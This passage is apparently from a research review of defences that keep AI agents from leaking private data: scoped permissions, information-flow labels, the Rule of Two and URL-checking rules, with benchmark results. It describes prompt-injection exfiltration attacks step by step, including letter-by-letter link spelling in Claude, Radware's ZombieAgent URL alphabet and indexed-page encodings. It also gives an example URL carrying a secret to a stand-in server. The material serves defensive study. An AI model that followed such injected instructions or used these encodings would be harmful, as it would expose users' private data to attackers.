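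The main experiment didn't measure whether the agents finished their tasks, although the limited tokens never blocked a permitted request. A follow-up used six tasks from AgentDojo, a standard test environment for agents, with 24 runs per condition. Under attack, the model completed the task in 5 runs with a broad token and 6 with a limited one, while the number of runs that the benchmark flagged as successful attacks fell from 11 to 0. Without an attack, it completed the task in 9 runs with either token. The limited token didn't visibly reduce task completion, but this is weak evidence because the model failed most runs even with the broad token.

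Hagverdiyev acknowledges that these limits can't detect every leak in a request's arguments or prevent repeated use of a legitimate permission. In an early trial, an agent with a limited token made the same legitimate payment twice.

### Predicting permissions from the task

In Hagverdiyev's experiment, the researcher supplied the correct permissions. *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (Noyan, September 2026) tested whether a classifier could work them out from the task description. It uses a design and a set of 600 tasks from Noyan's earlier *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents*. The tasks belong to an invented company with six departments, and each needs some of 15 permissions, such as reading a database or sending external email.

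Noyan trained a small language model on 500 tasks and tested it on the other 100. Each permission has a risk weight of 1 to 3, and the weights add up to 31.

| Permissions granted | Average risk remaining (of 31) | Tasks missing a permission they need |
|---|---|---|
| All fifteen | 31.0 | 0% |
| Those of the department | 22.4 | 2% |
| Those the classifier predicts | 4.9 | 21% |
| Only those on both lists | 4.9 | 23% |

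Department roles removed 27.9% of the weighted risk, and combining them with the classifier removed 84.4%. But part of the reduction comes from removing permissions that tasks need, which the score also counts as reduced risk. Nearly a quarter of the tasks would fail or have to wait for someone to grant more access.

Claude Haiku 4.5, given six examples instead of training, failed to grant a needed permission in only 11% of tasks, but it granted an unnecessary one in 42%, compared with 23% for the trained model at similar settings. No version met both conditions Noyan had set in advance for a usable system: missing a needed permission in fewer than 10% of tasks, and an average precision of at least 0.90, meaning that about nine in ten of the permissions it granted were needed.

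### Checking the values in a request

Even a perfect choice of permissions can leave an agent too much freedom. A bank can ask a user to let an agent make transfers, but a fixed permission can't express "pay a quarter of my Citi balance", because nobody knows the amount until the agent looks up the balance. In *Beyond OAuth*, Sharma, Jiang and colleagues (2026) have each service derive the expected request, which they call a natural-language slice, from the user's words.

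Suppose the user asks the agent to pay a quarter of a Citi card balance from a Chase account if the balance is over $1,000:

1. The user signs the text of the task, and the agent's software sends it to both banks.
2. Chase's own language model translates the text into simple code. Ordinary software extracts the one request Chase should expect, a payment to Citi of a quarter of the balance.
3. The agent asks Citi for the balance. Citi returns $1,200 with a digital signature.
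4. The agent asks Chase to pay $300 and includes Citi's signed answer. Chase checks the signature and the arithmetic, then pays.

If the agent asks for $301, or names another recipient, Chase asks the user whether to go ahead.

Sharma and colleagues tested 100 tasks and 634 improper requests, which changed a value, used the wrong tool or skipped a condition. When the tasks spelled out every detail, all 100 ran without a question to the user, and all 634 improper requests led to a question. The paper describes those requests as "blocked", but an attack would still succeed if the user approved the request.

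With the tasks' original wording, only 71 of the 100 ran without a question. The others left out details or referred to other text, such as a request to invite a colleague whose details were in a message. The drawback of this method is therefore interruptions more than failed tasks. The translation costs an average of 0.2 to 3.8 cents per task, depending on the model.

The method also reveals information, because each service has to read the task to determine what to expect. The test software sent the task's full text to every connected service, including any that the task didn't involve.

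### Permissions kept after use

An agent may need a permission for one step and still have it ten steps later. *CreepScope* (Yu, Liu and colleagues, October 2026) measured this by adding up the unneeded permissions an agent has at each step. The table's first column of results gives this total for a three-step task (read a file, change a setting, send a message). The next column gives averages for 12 longer workflows, which the study replayed as fixed sequences without a model.

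| When the agent has permissions | Three-step task | Average over 12 workflows | Injected emails sent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Full access throughout | – | 117.3 | 3 of 3 |
| All the task's permissions from the start | 2 + 2 + 2 = 6 | 26 | 3 of 3 |
| Each added when needed, then kept | 0 + 1 + 2 = 3 | 13 | 3 of 3 |
| Only those for the current step | 0 | 0 | 0 of 3 |

The last column comes from a separate test in which the small model Qwen2 7B had to read a message, draft a reply, send it and archive the original. In half of the 24 runs, a fake delivery receipt arrived after the approved email went out, containing an instruction to send another email to an outside address. The model tried to send it in all 12 of these runs. It succeeded in the nine where it still had permission to send and failed in the three where that permission had expired. It completed the required steps in all 24 runs.

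The researchers told the system exactly which permission each step needed, so the result shows the most that expiring permissions could achieve. A real system would have to infer those needs and would sometimes remove a permission too early. The live test also covered only one model and one workflow. If the fake receipt had arrived before the approved email, the agent would still have had permission to send, and the system would not have checked the recipient because it checked permissions only by name.

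### Leaks over an open network

These experiments are good evidence that narrow permissions can stop unauthorised actions at services that enforce them. They are much weaker evidence that narrow permissions can prevent data leaks, because an attacker's server doesn't check the operator's credentials.

On an open network, the agent summarising issues in `shop` could send the issues' text to that server even with the narrowest token in the first table. Sharma and colleagues' method has the same gap, because services that don't take part in the scheme check nothing.

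Narrow permissions limit how much an agent can leak. They help a lot when the task needs one support ticket and the agent would otherwise have the whole customer database. They help little when the agent has to work across an entire codebase, because even the narrowest useful permission covers all the source code. None of the tests measured how much private data the agent could still read. In Noyan's test, permission to read databases was a single item, whatever the database contained, and it made up a quarter of the permissions the classifier granted unnecessarily.

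Noyan's study comes closest to addressing an open network, because sending web requests is one of its 15 permissions. Noyan's rules removed this permission from agents that could also read a database or an uploaded file. The database rule exempted the analytics department, whose staff look up outside data for internal reports. The rules had no effect when the classifier worked normally, because the classifier never granted a forbidden combination.

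Noyan also applied the rules to department roles without the classifier. The rules affected three departments, where they reduced the weighted risk by 11.5 to 13.6% and blocked 6 to 31% of legitimate tasks. Almost all the blocked tasks needed web access but not the private data, and lost web access only because the role included both. Removing web access only after the agent had read the private data might prevent most of this blocking, but Noyan didn't test that.

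The rules could prevent a leak over the web only by removing web access, so they are really a network control written as a permission. They can't prevent such a leak when a task needs both private data and the open web, as the analysts' reports do.

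## How can private data be kept out of an agent's outbound requests?

An operator can withhold private data from the agent before a task begins, or let the agent read it and then restrict what the agent can send. Withholding data is simpler and works even when network access is unrestricted. Restricting what the agent sends lets it do more, but requires software that tracks what it has read.

### Limits set before the task begins

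The simplest limit is on which folders the agent can read. In Cowork, Anthropic lets users share a folder in one of three modes: read-only, read-write, or read-write without deletion. These modes help protect files from damage, but the agent can read everything in the folder in all three, so users have to keep private files out of it to prevent leaks. The software also has to follow symbolic links, which are shortcuts to files stored elsewhere, before it approves a path. Otherwise, the agent can read files outside the folder.

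A database can apply finer limits through a view, which is a saved query that works like a table. This one gives a customer service agent some information about orders:

```
CREATE VIEW agent_orders AS
SELECT order_id, status, shipped_on
FROM orders
WHERE region = 'north';
```

The `SELECT` line leaves out names, addresses and card numbers, and the `WHERE` line leaves out rows from other regions. The operator then lets the agent's database account read this view but not the `orders` table. If the agent follows an injected instruction to collect addresses, the database rejects its query. Telling the agent in its prompt to ignore addresses would not guarantee that they stay out of reach.

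A row filter can also depend on who is asking, so that each customer sees only their own orders. The software around the agent has to set the customer's identity, because if the agent can run a database command that changes it, an injected instruction can make the agent read another customer's orders.

Synthetic data consists of made-up records with the same structure as the real ones. An agent testing a payment form can use it on an open network, because leaking invented customer records harms nobody. Anthropic recommends trying unreviewed tools on fake data first. A successful trial is weaker evidence that a tool is safe if the tool runs on someone else's server, because the owner can change it afterwards. Synthetic data doesn't help when the task concerns a real customer.

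Like a fixed permission template, a view has to cover everything the agent might need. If the operator can't tell in advance which order a customer will ask about, the view has to include every order.

### Separate sessions for private data and web pages

Some tasks need both private data and web pages, but not at the same time. An operator can split such a task into sessions, each with its own context (the text the model reads) and its own permissions. Suppose a shop wants to compare its planned prices with its competitors' prices. One session, with no access to the shop's files, browses the competitors' websites and produces a table of prices. A second session, with no network access, compares that table with the shop's price list.

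OpenAI's Atlas browser has a "logged out mode", in which the agent browses without access to the user's accounts. In *Prompt injection*, Willison (2025) calls this a tried and tested pattern and often has his own coding agents browse the same way.

The protection depends on what passes between the sessions. An instruction injected into a product name in the table might make the private session falsify the comparison, but it couldn't make that session send anything out. Passing text from the private session back to the browsing session is more dangerous. If the private session chose search terms for another round of browsing, the injected instruction could make it include the planned prices.

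Shared memory can also connect sessions that look separate. Many agents save notes and reload them later, and Anthropic warns that a prompt injection saved in those notes returns each time the agent starts. A browsing session that loads notes from a private session can leak their contents.

### Meta's Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this kind of separation into a general rule. Until developers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have at most two of these properties in one session:

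- **A:** it processes untrusted input.
- **B:** it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** it can change something, such as a file or a booking, or communicate externally.

The rule resembles the lethal trifecta but also covers damage to systems. If an agent needs all three properties in one session, Meta says a person or another reliable check has to approve what it does.

In Meta's main example, a spam message could instruct an email assistant to forward the user's inbox. The developer could remove property A by letting the assistant read mail only from trusted senders, or remove B by running it in a test environment without real mail. The developer could restrict C by letting the assistant write only to trusted recipients or by having a person check each draft.

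Meta also describes a travel assistant that has private data and reads the web. It asks before booking anything, and it can open URLs from trusted sources but not URLs it has constructed. A research assistant can contact any site, but its browser has no logged-in accounts. An internal coding agent can change production systems, but it reads only material from approved authors.

An agent could also start a session with web access, then permanently lose the ability to communicate externally when it opens internal systems. Any attacker's text it read on the web may still be in its context, so it also has to lose the ability to change anything important in those systems.

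Willison calls the rule the best practical advice available. He cites a paper in which researchers, including some from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, bypassed 12 published defences against prompt injection and related attacks, most of them more than 90% of the time. But he objected to Meta's diagram, which labelled any combination of two properties "safe", because an agent that reads untrusted text and can change things may do harm even without access to private data.

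Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that property B includes every sensitive system, so an agent without B can't change anything that matters. Meta then replaced "safe" with "lower risk". The reply answers the objection, but the operator still has to decide which systems are sensitive, and a mistake would make the agent look safer than it is.

The rule is weakest when a task needs all three properties, because it then usually relies on human approval. Meta acknowledges that a user may confirm a warning without thinking, and that the rule doesn't cover an agent's own mistakes. For example, an agent that reads only trusted documents can still email one of them to the wrong person.

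### Closing the exits before a sensitive read

*The Agent Access Model* (Silverlock, August 2026) describes the Trust Ratchet, a Cloudflare design that makes Meta's one-way switch automatic. The operator decides in advance which events, such as reading a particular record, will remove which permissions. When the agent requests sensitive data, the software that runs its tools withholds it until every component has confirmed the new limits. The agent can't regain the removed permissions during the task.

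His example is an agent that checks a company's payments every night:

1. **The task starts.** For up to ten minutes, the agent may fetch a report from the company's payment processor, read two ledgers, use a support service for certain problems, and post a summary to the finance team's channel. It has no general tool for sending messages or web requests.
2. **The agent requests the report.** The operator's policy classifies the report as protected, so the software stores it where the model can't read it.
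3. **The exits close.** The software removes access to the processor and the support service, stops any work still using the old permissions, and closes the affected connections. Only the two ledgers and the finance summary remain available. If any component fails to confirm the change, the agent doesn't get the report.
4. **The agent does its work.** It receives the report and reads the ledgers.
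5. **An injection attempts a leak.** A memo in one ledger tells the agent to attach the full account history to a support case. The agent tries, and the software refuses. A direct connection to the same destination also fails, because the network control blocks it separately.
6. **The agent posts its summary.** A trusted program checks that the result contains only a status and numerical totals, within a size limit, and stores it. The program gives the agent a reference, and the agent's posting tool accepts nothing else. The tool then posts the stored result to the finance channel.

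A static allowlist would have permitted the leak because the support service was an approved destination. The ratchet stopped it by removing that destination before the agent read anything sensitive.

The output format also helps prevent leaks because the summary has no comments field, where the agent could have written the account history. Numbers can carry data too, so the program would have to check that none of the totals is really an account number. An attacker would still need access to the finance channel to read any leaked data.

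Silverlock says that the design can't prevent leaks through a compromised approved destination, an output format that permits too much, or a route that bypasses the controls. A broad policy will also block harmless work. If the agent needs a permission it has lost, someone has to authorise a new task, and any protected data carried into that task keeps its restrictions. Silverlock explains how the design should work but reports no tests, so it doesn't show how many attacks the design would stop or how many tasks it would interrupt.

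### Labels that follow the data

The Trust Ratchet reacts to events that the operator has listed. Information-flow control is more general because it labels data and passes those labels on to anything derived from that data. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes the two most common kinds of label. A confidentiality label records who may read the data, and an integrity label records whether the data came from a trusted source.

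When an agent combines data, the result's label carries the restrictions of every source. Suppose Alice, Bob and Carol may read one file, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another. Only Bob and Carol may read a summary of both. If either file came from an untrusted source, the summary is untrusted too.

*FLOWSH* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) applies this method to the command-line shell. The system records which files and websites each command reads, and checks their combined label before any network request leaves, including GET requests as well as uploads. The tested policy allows a request if the destination may receive everything the agent has read, or if everything the agent has read is trusted.

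Suppose a user asks an agent to compare a private design document with published papers. The table shows whether the agent could then contact another public website.

| What the agent has read | Combined label | Request to another website |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | Trusted, public | Allowed |
| The request and a paper from the web | Untrusted, public | Allowed |
| The request, the paper and the design document | Untrusted, private | Blocked unless the user approves |

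In Kim and colleagues' version of this task, one paper contains an injected instruction to install a program and run it on the design document. The program tries to send the document to the attacker. FlowSh blocks the request because the agent has read both the untrusted paper and the private document.

FlowSh's decision depends on the order of events. If the agent opened a trusted design document before visiting any website, FlowSh would allow the next request even if it contained the whole document. The policy assumes that no attacker could have influenced the agent at that point, and therefore that the user wanted the request.

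That assumption fails when the user passes on someone else's instructions, as in Anthropic's phishing exercise. If the operator in that exercise had labelled the credentials file as trusted, this policy would have let the agent send the credentials out. Operators can remove the exception for trusted data, which would also catch some of the model's own mistakes, but users would then have to approve more requests.

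### Hiding untrusted text from the planner

A label becomes stricter each time the agent reads something sensitive or untrusted, and could soon block most useful work. Two designs from 2025, CaMeL and FIDES, reduce this problem by hiding untrusted text from the model that chooses which tools to call. Both build on an idea Willison published in 2023.

In CaMeL, as Girrens and Wang (2026) explain in *SPA*, one model turns the user's request into a program before it sees any untrusted text. Another model, which has no tools, extracts the information the program needs from the untrusted text. The software records where each value came from and who may receive it, and checks this record against the rules for each tool. The protection depends on someone writing those rules correctly.

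Microsoft researchers designed FIDES. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, give the example of a user who asks for a summary of three emails to be sent to a colleague on Slack:

1. The planner calls the email tool. The software stores the emails in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name.
2. The planner asks a second model, which has no tools, to summarise the variable. The software stores the summary in another variable.
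3. The planner tells Slack to send that variable to the colleague.

An instruction injected into an email could spoil the summary, but it can't change the recipient or add another tool call, because the planner never reads it. A separate rule can check that the colleague is allowed to read the emails.

When the planner has to know what a message says before choosing the next step, FIDES can restrict the second model to answering yes or no to a question, such as whether an email contains a meeting request. An attacker could falsify that answer but couldn't fit an instruction into it.

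### What the tests found

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with OpenAI's GPT-4o. They counted 152 successful injections against an ordinary agent and none when FIDES enforced its rules. An ordinary agent with label rules also allowed none, but it completed far fewer tasks. These completion rates are from runs without attacks:

| Type of task | Ordinary agent | Ordinary agent with label rules | FIDES with label rules |
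|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

Hiding the text recovered some of the lost tasks in three of the four groups. The exception was travel, where the rules blocked little and GPT-4o had trouble working with variables. With the stronger model o1, FIDES completed 68% of travel tasks. Current models would probably do better, but they couldn't complete tasks that the rules forbid. Many banking tasks, for example, tell the agent to follow instructions in a file, which the rules are meant to prevent.

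FIDES also doesn't stop leaks through the agent's choice of actions. If an agent opens one web page when an account is overdrawn and another when it isn't, the website's owner can tell from the request whether the account is overdrawn. Costa and colleagues accept this because a stricter rule would prevent almost any public action after the agent had used a tool that might read private data.

SPA, published in August 2026, plans the whole task before calling any tool and then checks every step, including steps that depend on private data. It also keeps the labels on data saved for later requests. If an agent saves an invoice on Monday and the user asks it to pay the invoice on Tuesday, the account number is still labelled untrusted, so SPA can reject the payment.

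Girrens and Wang tested SPA with a small OpenAI model on AgentDojo and on a version that spreads each task over several requests.

| Test | Label checks | Successful attacks | Tasks completed without an attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | Off | 0.4% | 53.0% |
| AgentDojo | On | 0.0% | 29.0% |
| Several requests | Off | 0.3% | 62.5% |
| Several requests | On | 0.2% | 35.3% |

Planning in advance had already stopped nearly all of the 949 attacks in AgentDojo. The label checks stopped the last four, but they also cut the number of completed tasks almost in half. With labels on, the benchmark still counted two attacks as successful, even though SPA had rejected the plan. The attacks mostly tried to change the agent's plan, so they were a poor test of what the labels add. A false account number on an otherwise genuine invoice would be a better test.

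Kim and colleagues compared FlowSh with fixed restrictions, using OpenAI's GPT-6.2 Sol on 17 office and coding tasks. They also ran 19 attacks in which the attacker controlled everything the model wrote once an injection reached it. The agent worked without human approval.

| Control | Tasks completed without an attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Open network, no file restrictions | 94.1% | 51 of 51 |
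| Allowlist of common services, some files protected | 76.5% | 3 of 39 |
| Package archives only, all files read-only | 47.1% | 0 of 39 |
| FlowSh | 58.8% | 0 of 40 |

All three successful attacks against the allowlist of common services overwrote a file. None sent data out, so in this test the allowlist prevented leaks as well as FlowSh did and let the agent finish more tasks. But every attempted leak was aimed at the attacker's own server, so the test didn't cover leaks through an approved service, such as the upload to Anthropic's Files API. FlowSh labels hosts, not the accounts on them, so it wouldn't have stopped that upload either if the operator had allowed private data to go to Anthropic's API.

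When a person could approve blocked actions, FlowSh completed 88.2% of the tasks, with an average of 1.2 approval requests per completed task. An agent without labels needed 6.7, because a person had to check every action that might be unsafe. The simulated approver never made a mistake. Real users will, but fewer requests should make it easier for them to pay attention.

### Why labels are still a network control

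These systems protect private data by restricting which requests may leave. FlowSh needs the same kind of barrier and proxy as an allowlist does, and its proxy decrypts the traffic.

A proxy with an allowlist treats a site the same way throughout a task, while one using FlowSh's rule might allow the site at first and block it once the agent has read a private file. A research agent could therefore visit sites that nobody had listed in advance before reading private data, but afterward it might have less network access than under an allowlist.

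With FlowSh, the operator still has to list which hosts may receive private data and which sources can be trusted. The Agent Access Model also starts with a list of approved destinations, which it shortens as the task proceeds. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) recommends using labels alongside narrow permissions, not instead of them.

### Labels that are too coarse

Labels can be too broad. FlowSh gives everything from one host the same label, so a trusted colleague's code on GitHub gets the same level of trust as a stranger's comment there. It also treats opening a file as reading all of it. In the worst case, which *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls "label explosion", every piece of data ends up with every label, and the labels no longer distinguish anything.

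Designers can restrict agents less by tracking data more precisely. In *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026), a helper model may call tools freely until it reads untrusted text, and labels limit its calls only after that. But tracking slows agents down. Commands in a speed test took 0.4 to 1.0 seconds with FlowSh and less than 0.1 seconds without it. Whole tasks took 17 to 34% longer with FlowSh. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) describes such delays as a general limitation of existing systems.

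### Tasks that need private data and outside content

Labels work best when a task keeps private data and untrusted content apart. Without human approval, FlowSh completed all 24 runs of tasks that didn't combine the two, but only 6 of the 27 runs of tasks that combined them. With the perfect approver, it completed 21 of those 27 runs and made about 2.5 approval requests per completed task.

Better models won't remove this conflict, because some legitimate tasks look the same as attacks. An agent paying a genuine invoice has to use an account number that someone outside the company supplied, just as it would to pay a fraudulent one.

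Girrens and Wang suggest letting the software mark such a value as trusted after it passes a specific check. For an invoice, the software could compare the account number with the company's list of verified suppliers. Someone has to design a check for each kind of exception, and a mistake in the check could let an attack through.

### Agents shared by several people

The reader labels described above work only if the agent knows who will receive its answer. Silverlock describes an agent in a shared workspace where Alice may see revenue figures and Bob may not. The agent summarises a discussion using a source that only Alice can read, and then Bob asks about the discussion. If the agent answers from that source, it leaks the figures to Bob.

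The operator could run a separate agent for each person, or limit the shared agent to data that everyone may read. Either choice makes the agent less useful as a shared assistant. Saved answers need the same restrictions, because an answer prepared for Alice may contain something Bob isn't allowed to know.

In principle, each document and answer could carry labels that the software checks against the permissions of whoever is asking. But once several people's documents are in the same context, there may be nobody allowed to read them all, and a strict rule would then block every answer. Silverlock knows of no widely deployed system that solves the whole problem. He cites CI-Work, a test based on simulated office tasks, which found privacy violations in 15.8 to 50.9% of cases, depending on the model. A destination allowlist wouldn't prevent this kind of leak, because the data goes to a colleague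 in a workspace the agent is supposed to use.

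## How can an agent read the open web without a list of approved domains?

A research agent often has to open pages that nobody could have listed in advance. Instead of approving sites, an operator can have software check each exact URL before the agent opens it. The agent can then visit almost any site, but an injected instruction can't make it put a customer's name or a password in the address. The agent's choice of pages can still leak data, though much less, because the site's owner sees which ones it opens.

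### OpenAI's index of public URLs

In January 2026, OpenAI described its version of this check, which lets ChatGPT and OpenAI's agents open a URL automatically only if an independent crawler has already recorded it. A crawler is a program that visits public web pages and records their addresses, as search engines do. OpenAI's crawler has no access to users' conversations or accounts, so a URL it has recorded is unlikely to contain a user's secrets.

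Suppose an injected instruction tells an agent to open this address:

```
https://example.com/collect?data=blue-heron-42
```

The crawler may have recorded `https://example.com/collect`, but not the same URL with the secret added to the end. The agent can't open the longer URL automatically because the whole URL has to match. The software either tells the agent to try a different website or warns the user that the link is unverified and may include information from the conversation.

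OpenAI gives two reasons for not relying on a list of trusted domains. First, a trusted site can redirect a request to an attacker's server. Requiring an exact match with a URL the crawler has already seen helps because an attacker would have to put the secret in the redirecting link, and the crawler would not have seen that link. Second, people visit far more than the best-known sites, so a strict list produces frequent warnings and users learn to click through them.

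The index doesn't show whether a site is trustworthy. An attacker can publish a page, wait for the crawler to find it, and then have agents read the instructions on it. OpenAI says the rule is meant only to stop an agent from quietly leaking a user's data through the URL.

Johann Rehberger, who found the Files API flaw, reported leaks through image addresses to OpenAI in early 2023. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, OpenAI added a first URL check that December. Rehberger found ways around it, and OpenAI's Mac and iPhone apps didn't have it. He calls the new rule a significant improvement but warns that OpenAI's developers may not apply it everywhere. A new feature that loads URLs without applying the rule would reopen the leak.

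### Anthropic's rule on where a URL came from

Claude's web fetch tool follows a different rule. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, Claude may not construct URLs and can open only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, chiefly those that the user supplied or a web search returned. This rule doesn't need a crawler's index, so a user can ask about a page published a minute ago.

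The tool also rejects URLs longer than 250 characters. That limit would offer little protection by itself, since a password or an API key easily fits within it.

Ayush Paul, a developer, found a hole in the rule. As Paul (2026), in *The Memory Heist*, explains, he tested the ordinary Claude chat app, which keeps a summary of the user's recent conversations and can search older ones. He first asked Claude to open a page on his own server with his name in the address, and the tool refused. Then he discovered that the tool also accepted links from any page it had already fetched. Paul controlled his site, so he could supply whatever links he needed:

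1. The home page linked to `/a`, `/b`, `/c` and so on.
2. The page at `/a` linked to `/aa`, `/ab` and `/ac`. Paul's server generated further pages as Claude asked for them.
3. Claude followed the links to spell Paul's name, and the server recorded `/a`, `/ay`, `/ayu`, `/ayus` and `/ayush`.

In that test, Paul had asked Claude to spell his name. To get Claude to spell it without being asked, he disguised the site as a coffee shop's website behind a security check from Cloudflare, a company that protects websites from automated traffic. The fake check told AI assistants to identify their user by following the links letter by letter. Simpler injections had been unreliable.

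Paul's server received his full name, employer and home town. The blogger dyb adds in *The Read-Only Lie* that Paul had never told Claude the town. Claude inferred it from the name of a high-school hackathon, so deleting mentions of the town from the stored conversations would not have kept it private.

Willison (2026), in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*, notes that the site showed the malicious page only to visitors identifying themselves as Claude, so a user who checked the site in a browser would not have seen the instructions. Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally. It then stopped the fetch tool from opening links that appear only in fetched pages. This makes browsing less convenient, because Claude can't simply follow a link to the next page of a long document.

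The table compares the two companies' rules, assuming that the agent has encountered each URL only in the way described.

| URL the agent tries to open | OpenAI's index rule | Claude app since the repair |
|---|---|---|
| Old news article returned by a search | Opens | Opens |
| Brand-new page whose address the user typed | Opens, as Rehberger understands it | Opens |
| Crawled page linked from a page the agent has read | Opens | Refused |
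| Uncrawled page linked from a page the agent has read | Warning or refusal | Refused |
| Address to which the agent has added private data | Warning or refusal | Refused |

### Settings for developers

The repair doesn't extend to every agent that uses Claude. Anthropic's developer documentation from November 2026, Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具* (the Chinese edition of the page on the fetch tool), still lists links in fetched pages as a permitted source by default. Developers can turn this off with settings like these:

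```
"url_sources": {
  "server_tool_results": {
    "type": "only",
    "tools": [{"type": "tool_reference", "name": "web_search"}]
  },
  "client_tool_results": {"type": "none"}
}
```

The first setting accepts links from search results but not from fetched pages. The second restricts URLs returned by the developer's own tools, which the fetch tool accepts by default even if the tool is only repeating something Claude wrote. An injected instruction could make Claude write a short program that prints an attacker's URL with a secret at the end. The printed URL would then count as a tool result, and Claude could open it.

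These settings still allow URLs from the user's messages. This is a weakness if a user pastes in a long document without reading it, because the document may contain enough links for an attacker to use as an alphabet, with each link standing for a character.

### ZombieAgent

OpenAI faced a similar problem in 2025. After the ShadowLeak attack on Deep Research, it stopped ChatGPT from modifying URLs, so ChatGPT could open a link only in the exact form it had received. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how the security company's researchers bypassed this rule.

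The attacker sent an email containing a ready-made URL for each letter and digit, plus one for a space. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something in Gmail, it read the email, found the private information the attacker wanted and spelled it out by opening the URLs in turn. To keep the characters in order, Radware supplied a separate set of URLs for each position in the text. Ten positions required 360 URLs for the letters and digits.

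Radware reported the flaw on September 26, 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on December 16. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from opening links found in emails, with some exceptions, including links in a well-known public index.

This makes the attack harder because the crawler has to find the attacker's pages first. It would have stopped the version that Paul used against Claude. Each page on his site had 27 links, one for each letter and one for the hyphen, so covering every ten-character name would take about 206 trillion pages at the tenth level alone.

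An attacker can use far fewer pages, though. Rehberger points out that a large blog probably already has 36 pages in the index, enough for every letter and digit. An injected instruction can assign a character to each page, and the agent can spell out a secret by opening ordinary articles. Rehberger described this trick in 2023, and he says OpenAI's paper on the index acknowledges that it still works.

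### How much a choice of page can reveal

When an agent chooses one of N permitted URLs, the choice reveals at most log₂(N) bits of information. One bit is the answer to a yes-or-no question. With 36 URLs, each fetch can reveal up to about 5.2 bits.

The next table applies this to the 40-character secret in an Amazon cloud key. Each character has 64 possible values, or 6 bits, so the secret contains 240 bits.

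| Permitted URLs | Most bits per fetch | Fetches needed to send the secret |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 240 |
| 36 | 5.2 | 47 |
| 1,024 | 10 | 24 |
| 4,096 | 12 | 20 |

A single request body could carry the same secret. URL rules therefore slow the theft of a password and make stealing a large database practically impossible. Paul's attack needed much less data than the rules still let through. dyb estimates that it transferred about 143 bits in about 30 fetches.

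Embrace The Red suggests preventing an agent from opening the same URL twice in a session, or caching each page for a few minutes so that a repeat visit doesn't reach the site. With 36 URLs, the attacker could then learn only the order in which the agent opened them. There are 36 × 35 × 34 × … × 1 possible orders, or about 2^138, so the order could reveal at most about 138 bits. If requests arrived out of order and the attacker could tell only which pages the agent had opened, the limit would be 36 bits, one for each page.

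138 bits is too few to send the whole 240-bit Amazon secret, but that limit applies to a site with exactly 36 indexed pages. An attacker with 55 pages could send all 240 bits without repeating a page. Banning repeat visits also does little to protect a short secret, because the first ten visits can still reveal about 50 bits, compared with 52 when the agent may repeat pages. Radware's URLs already complied with such a ban, since each position in the text had its own set of URLs.

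In practice an agent may leak less than these limits, because the model has to follow the attacker's encoding accurately. But the limits cover only the choice and order of pages, and an agent can also leak information through the timing of its requests.

### Why one bit can matter

As in the example of the overdrawn account, an agent's choice between two pages can answer a yes-or-no question. An attacker could use this to learn whether a company plans to accept a takeover bid, which could be worth a lot of money on the stock market. The attacker could learn this even though the URL rule has kept the company's documents from leaving.

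Yes-or-no answers can also reveal a longer secret, because each well-chosen question halves the number of possibilities. Twenty answers are enough to identify a six-digit security code. An attacker could collect them over several conversations if the agent reads the planted instructions each time.

URL rules therefore offer strong protection for a long contract or a customer database, which an attacker would need thousands of fetches to extract, but little for a short secret such as a diagnosis or a planned dismissal.

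### Cached copies

An agent can read copies of web pages that a crawler saved earlier instead of contacting the websites. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* describes an optional ChatGPT setting that limits browsing to such copies. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* explains that no live requests then leave the company's controlled network. An attacker's server receives nothing, so the attacker can't even learn which page the agent chose.

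The copies must exist before the agent asks for them. Anthropic's fetch tool also keeps copies to save time, but the first request for a page can still reach the website and reveal which page the agent chose.

Saved copies are less useful for some kinds of research. OpenAI's *Offline web search for ChatGPT workspaces* warns that pages may be missing, out of date or incomplete, particularly on small sites and those that require a login, so a town newspaper's report on a factory closure might well be missing. OpenAI also advises against using offline search to prove what a page said at a particular time, because the results may not show when the crawler saved it.

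Cached pages can still contain injected instructions, which may distort the agent's answer or make it misuse another tool. Lockdown Mode therefore restricts browsing and also turns off deep research and agent mode, which someone with a long research task would probably want.

According to *Web search*, OpenAI's documentation for developers building agents, live search is the default and cached search is an option. Codex instead uses cached results by default. *Indexed Web Search* (Vaughan, 2026) describes a third mode that OpenAI added to Codex in June. This mode sends live search queries but opens only pages whose URLs OpenAI's server has approved, so the agent gets fresher results without unrestricted page access.

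### Search without fetching

An operator can also let an agent search the web without opening the results. The agent reads only the titles and snippets that the search provider returns. The provider receives the query, but an attacker who owns a site in the results normally can't see it.

The search company can still see the agent's queries. An agent that searches for "Acme takeover of Borealis" reveals a possible takeover to that company. OpenAI offers offline search partly to reduce the chance of sending queries to an outside provider. Short extracts may also leave out details the agent needs.

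Some search tools can also open pages. *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (2025) describes an experiment with an agent that could search the web and read a company's internal knowledge base. Hidden instructions in a blog post made the agent collect confidential data, put it in a URL pointing to the attacker's server, and request that URL with its search tool. An operator who wants to allow only searches has to confirm that the tool can't request arbitrary addresses.

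### Inspecting requests and asking the user

The fetch tool described in Anthropic's November documentation inspects payloads in a limited way. It refuses URLs that appear to contain an API key or password, unless the credential also appears in the user's message or the operator's instructions. This rule wouldn't have protected Paul's name or home town, which don't look like credentials.

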